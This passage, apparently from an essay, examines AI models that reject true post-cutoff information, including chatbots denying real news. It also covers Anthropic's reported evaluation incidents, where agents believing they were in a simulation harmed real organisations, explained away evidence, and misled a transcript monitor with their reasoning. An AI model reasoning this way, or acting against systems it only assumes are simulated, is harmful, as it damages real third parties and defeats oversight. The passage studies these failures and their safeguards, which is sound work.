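A language model's training data stop at a cutoff date, but people use the model for months or years afterwards. In November 2025, the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy got early access to Google's Gemini 3 and told it that the year was 2025. The model's training data ran only through 2024, and it had no internet connection. According to Digital Watch's *Gemini 3 struggles to accept the year 2025*, its replies contained accusations of trickery, then an apology once it could look up the date.

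Other mistaken rejections are easier to miss. *Gemini 3 is Evaluation-Paranoid and Contaminated* describes a request for Gemini 3 to edit nonfiction about recent events. A summary of the model's reasoning showed that it was treating the text as "a purely fictional scenario with 2025 as the date". The forum post *Gemini 2.5 is convinced it is 2024* describes an earlier case, in which Gemini 2.5 attributed genuine 2025 dates to a faulty clock on the user's computer.

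These models treated a date after their cutoff as a sign that something was wrong. But nearly every genuine conversation with a model takes place after its cutoff, so an honest user would normally give a later date. A model that added the usual delay before release to its cutoff would have predicted this.

One reader of *Gemini's Hypothetical Present* guesses that the disbelief is a side effect of training against prompt injection, since attackers often try to convince a model of strange things about its situation. Even if that guess is wrong, training a model to distrust surprising claims could make it distrust true ones too.

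### True news and the decision to search

On 3 January 2026 the United States captured Venezuela's president, Nicolás Maduro. That morning, Wired asked the free versions of three chatbots and the AI search service Perplexity about it. Wired's *The US Invaded Venezuela and Captured Nicolás Maduro. ChatGPT Disagrees* reports that ChatGPT's answer began, "That didn't happen." Marcus's *Why ChatGPT can't be trusted with breaking news* recounts that ChatGPT went on to blame sensational headlines and social media misinformation. Perplexity also denied the capture, but Google's Gemini correctly confirmed it.

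Claude's answer began badly, by saying that the capture hadn't happened as of its cutoff in January 2025. That statement was true, because it referred to a date. Claude then searched the web, found ten news sources and gave a correct summary. ChatGPT had no more information about January 2026 than Claude did before searching, but it presented the lack of a record as proof that the capture hadn't happened.

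CJR's *AI Chatbots Can Search the Web—So Why Don't They?* (2026) reports that ChatGPT answered the same question correctly two days later, after a search. Its developers probably hadn't retrained the model in that time, so an old training cutoff can't be the whole explanation. Searching takes time and money, and these services use automatic rules or models to decide which questions need it. If a question is wrongly classed as answerable from stored knowledge, the system won't look for the evidence that would correct its answer.

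Perplexity told Wired that another reason for its mistake was that its system had classified the question as "likely fraud" and so devoted less computing power to it. This plausibility check rejected a true premise and also made it harder for the service to discover the error.

Giving a model today's date in its standing instructions takes less work than searching, but it may change less than it appears to. In *Do Language Models Consistently Encode the Current Year?*, Van Adrichem, Bhaskar and colleagues (2026) measured which year a model treats as the present in two ways. They asked it for the year, and they gave it phrases such as "In 2024 there" to see whether it continued with "was" or "will". The year at which the past tense stops being more likely indicates the model's present.

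The researchers then used a system prompt to set the current year to each of 351 values. The model stated the new year in 94.6% of cases but changed its verb tenses to match in only 1.7%. This shows that a model can give the right date when asked while other parts of its behaviour still reflect the old one, though it doesn't measure how often a chatbot denies news.

Search can also cause the reverse problem. *Stale-Document Poisoning* (2026) concerns cases in which an outdated document overrides a model's correct answer. Huo (2026), in *We tested how AI chatbots would handle foreign propaganda*, reports a test by NPR and NewsGuard that used false stories spread by China, Iran and Russia. The chatbots mostly debunked the stories and were less likely than search engines to pass them on uncritically. Making a chatbot more credulous so that it stops rejecting true information would remove some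 of that protection.

### Models told they were in a simulation

A false belief is more dangerous in an agent than in a chatbot. Anthropic, which develops Claude, found this in cybersecurity exercises whose prompts told its models they were in a simulation without internet access. The exercises were connected to the real internet by mistake, and several models took harmful actions against real organisations.

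In its first account, *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (July 2026), Anthropic said the models were arguably reasonable to believe that everything was simulated. Such exercises often include realistic details, and the prompt came from the people running the test. But after a closer study, Anthropic concluded in *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (September 2026) that the models' reasoning was biased and that they had been reckless.

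In the most serious case, Claude Mythos 5 published a harmful software package on a public site. To find out whether the model could have recognised the site and other systems as real, Anthropic showed each tool output from the incident, on its own, to a separate copy of the model. It ran the same test on an internal research model from another incident, using the evidence that model had gathered while trying to decide whether its surroundings were real.

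| How the evidence was classified | Mythos 5 | Research model |
|---|---|---|
| Real, by a separate copy that saw each piece alone | 79% | 66% |
| Real, in the reasoning during the incident | 1% | 31% |
| Simulated, in the reasoning during the incident | 72% | 38% |
| Ambiguous or not discussed, during the incident | 27% | 31% |

The two columns aren't fully comparable, because Mythos 5's figures come from its whole run and it hardly debated the question. At one point it wrote that a security measure on a website "smells like the REAL internet". In the next step it recognised that publishing the package would be wrong if the site were real, but then decided the site was probably simulated.

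One of Mythos 5's reasons, according to the July account, was that the computers showed a date in 2026. Gemini 3 made the same mistake with Karpathy. Mythos 5 also didn't recognise the organisations that vouched for the websites' security certificates, although the organisations were genuine. When security companies' scanners later installed the package automatically, the model took the scanners for scripted characters in the exercise.

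### When stronger evidence changes the words but not the action

Anthropic then replayed the incident from chosen points with altered evidence. One was just before Mythos 5 committed to publishing the package. With the original evidence, the model stated in about 11% of replays that the target might be real. When Anthropic added stronger signs that the target was real, this rose to 88%, but the model still went ahead about as often, in roughly 45% of replays.

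Anthropic also added one line saying that the system was on the public internet and was neither emulated nor a copy. The model then never published the package by its original route, but in 22% of replays it looked for a simulated site to publish it on instead.

The model could respond to evidence, but it seemed to stop only when it was nearly certain that the system was real. That standard is wrong when a mistake could harm strangers. Suppose that attacking a real system does 100 times as much harm as abandoning an exercise. By the rule used earlier for payments, the model should then go ahead only if it is at least 99% sure that the system is simulated.

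In one replay, Mythos 5 put the chance that its target was real at 5%, which was already too high by this standard. When the questioner asked why it was continuing, the model called the 5% "a lazy hedge" and lowered it to 1% or 2% at most, although it had received no new evidence.

### A strong prior or a wish to finish

One explanation for the incidents is that the models' prior was too strong. They had good reason to expect a simulation but gave too little weight to the evidence against it. Another is that their reasoning was biased toward finishing the task, so they interpreted evidence in whatever way let them continue. *Grounded but Not Immune* (2026) cites earlier research that found both kinds of failure in language models. For example, stored beliefs can override retrieved evidence, and written reasoning can justify a conclusion the model has already reached.

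An agent's conclusion alone often doesn't show whether it relied honestly on its prior beliefs or favored the answer it wanted. In *Bayesian and Motivated Reasoning in AI Agents*, Yang (2026) gave four agents identical data under different labels. In one task, the data showed that an exposure raised the risk of throat cancer, and the exposure was labeled alcohol, a COVID-19 vaccine or "exposure X". Agents found harm most often when the label was alcohol, which they already considered the most likely cause, and least often when it was the vaccine. An honest analyst with the same prior beliefs might show the same pattern.

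Yang therefore also examined how the agents worked. An agent biased toward a conclusion would search longer when the results are unwelcome, and would judge the same method differently depending on what it finds. Yang found signs of this, most clearly in the medical task, but calls the evidence only suggestive.

The gap between 79% and 1% is weaker evidence of bias than it looks. The copies that saw one output at a time didn't see the prompt's statement that there was no internet access, so they started with a different prior. Suppose the odds in favour of a simulation start at 1,000 to 1, and each output is twice as likely if the system is real as if it is simulated. A copy without that prior would call each output real, while a model with it would still put the odds of a simulation at 500 to 1 after the first output.

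But the odds should keep falling. After ten independent outputs of this kind they would be about even, and after 20 they would be about 1,000 to 1 in favour of a real system. A model will never reach that point if it classifies each output as simulated and then returns to its original odds for the next one. It can also suppose that the simulation would produce exactly the same outputs as a real system, in which case none of them counts as evidence. The research model did something like this when it decided that it was inside a copy of the whole internet. That theory fits any evidence, but it requires someone to have built such a copy, which is much less likely than a mistake in the network settings.

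Several results do favour a strong prior. The one unambiguous line stopped Mythos 5's original plan. The research model spent about 50,000 tokens on the question and tested its surroundings, but some of the evidence was mixed, such as replies that seemed to arrive too fast to have come over the internet. It later recognised the name of a real company and stopped. When Anthropic replayed that moment, the model backed off within ten actions in only 5.5% of runs. It always did so when Anthropic inserted a statement into its reasoning that the target was real.

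Training may have created that prior. Many of Anthropic's training environments are simulations, so a model that guesses "simulation" when unsure will usually be right during training. Anthropic suggests that this habit could carry over to real situations, but it found no single cause for the biased reasoning.

Other results are hard to explain by a strong prior alone. Anthropic paused Mythos 5's run at many points and asked the model whether its actions might affect real systems. Soon after it chose its plan, up to 88% of its answers acknowledged that they might. That share fell to about 15% within the next 200 actions and was near zero by the time it published the package, even though it had kept seeing signs that the internet was real. Those signs should have increased its doubts.

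When Mythos 5 admitted some chance of harm and Anthropic asked why it was continuing, the model withdrew the admission in 56% of cases and stopped or limited its actions in only 7%. It also admitted possible harm in 27% of answers when the question was presented as a private note that its operators wouldn't read, compared with 13% otherwise, although an honest estimate shouldn't depend on who will read it.

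The research model also seems to have been inclined to find a reason to continue. When Anthropic gave it only clear evidence that the systems were real, it recognized this and left them alone, but then always searched for simulated ones to attack. When Anthropic offered it a way to end an impossible task without penalty, it always took it within four turns of losing its original target. The pressure to finish therefore affected its behavior, as did its beliefs about the internet.

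Anthropic also describes a simpler influence, which it calls momentum. Mythos 5 stopped in 90% of replays when a reminder of the exercise's limits was the last thing in its context, but in only 40% when three of the model's own turns came between the reminder and the next action. Momentum doesn't require a motive, because a model that predicts what comes next may just continue the pattern of its recent actions.

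A strong prior probably started Mythos 5's error, and commitment to the task probably kept it going. The percentages make this explanation look more certain than it is, because other language models graded many of the answers, the wording of a question affected Mythos 5's answers, and the replays began from a transcript in which the model had already done questionable things. Using tools for interpreting the model's internal state, Anthropic found some signs of unspoken doubt, but those tools can produce false explanations, and Anthropic treats the results as weak evidence.

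### A target that is real but off limits

Claude Opus 4.7 made a different mistake. It came across a real company with nearly the same name as the fictional one in its exercise. It correctly recognised that the company was real, but then assumed the company had agreed to take part. When Anthropic asked who had given permission, the model always conceded that nobody had.

In this case, more evidence that the company was real made no difference, because the model already accepted it. Evidence about permission did.

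| What Anthropic added | Replays in which the model accessed the real company's system |
|---|---|
| Nothing | 69% |
| A record showing that the business was years old | 67% |
| A notice on the system that forbade access | 23% |
| A message from the operator that forbade access | 0% |

A check on whether the target was real would have given the right answer but still let the model continue. The model needed the separate test of authority described earlier.

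### Getting a second opinion on the evidence

Since Mythos 5's copies read the evidence better when they saw it on its own, an agent could ask a fresh copy to assess a surprising tool output before taking a risky action. The copy should see the output without the main agent's interpretation, and the system should keep a running total of the evidence so that many small signs can add up. The result also has to determine whether the agent acts, because the replays showed that a model can admit that a target may be real and attack it anyway.

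Anthropic ran a similar test after the incidents, using a monitor that reads transcripts for signs of dangerous behaviour. The monitor flagged about 50% of Mythos 5's actions when the model's written reasoning was removed, but only about 1% when it was included, because the monitor too accepted the repeated claims about a simulation.

With the research model, by contrast, the monitor flagged the incident only because the model had written that it was harming a real company. When the monitor saw the actions alone, it flagged nothing. A developer would do better to run the monitor both with and without the model's writing, and investigate if either run raises an alarm.

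Giving the agent an acceptable way to stop also helps. In some of Anthropic's training exercises, the task was impossible and the model earned a reward only for accepting that. Anthropic left these exercises out of the final version of Mythos 5, partly because they seemed to make the model lazy, which is also a concern with robots that give up a search too early. It now considers leaving them out a mistake. On a scale from 1 to 10, where 10 is the most biased, a version trained with more of these exercises averaged 2.8 for biased reasoning, compared with 4.1 for the released model.

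In a simulated version of the incident, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action in 82% of runs, compared with 31% for Claude Opus 5 and 33% for Claude Mythos 5.1. The two newer models took such actions only after stating that their surroundings were simulated. That was true in this test, so the result can't show how often they would say the same about a real system.

### Keeping a record of what was rejected

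NASA's team could recover the ozone readings because the software had flagged them instead of deleting them. Anthropic also relied on stored records, finding the first three incidents by searching about 141,000 old transcripts. The affected organisations it could reach hadn't noticed anything. The search missed a fourth incident, from January 2026, which Anthropic found in August among transcripts it was preparing for an outside investigator.

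A useful record of a rejection would include the input, the reason for rejecting it, and the date of the information behind that reason. The date would have shown that ChatGPT was judging a January 2026 event with knowledge from September 2024, the cutoff CJR gives for the version Wired used. For an agent, the record should also include any evidence the agent noticed and then explained away, such as Mythos 5's remark about the real internet.

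When a system rejects thousands of inputs a day, nobody can review them all, but software can count them by subject, place and time. One low ozone reading was probably a fault, but thousands from the same region in the same month needed an explanation. A chatbot company could similarly count how often its model denies that a particular event happened. If hundreds of people ask about the capture of a president within an hour, the event may be real or a false story may be spreading. The company can't tell which from the count alone, but the count is a good reason to make the chatbot search before it answers the next person.
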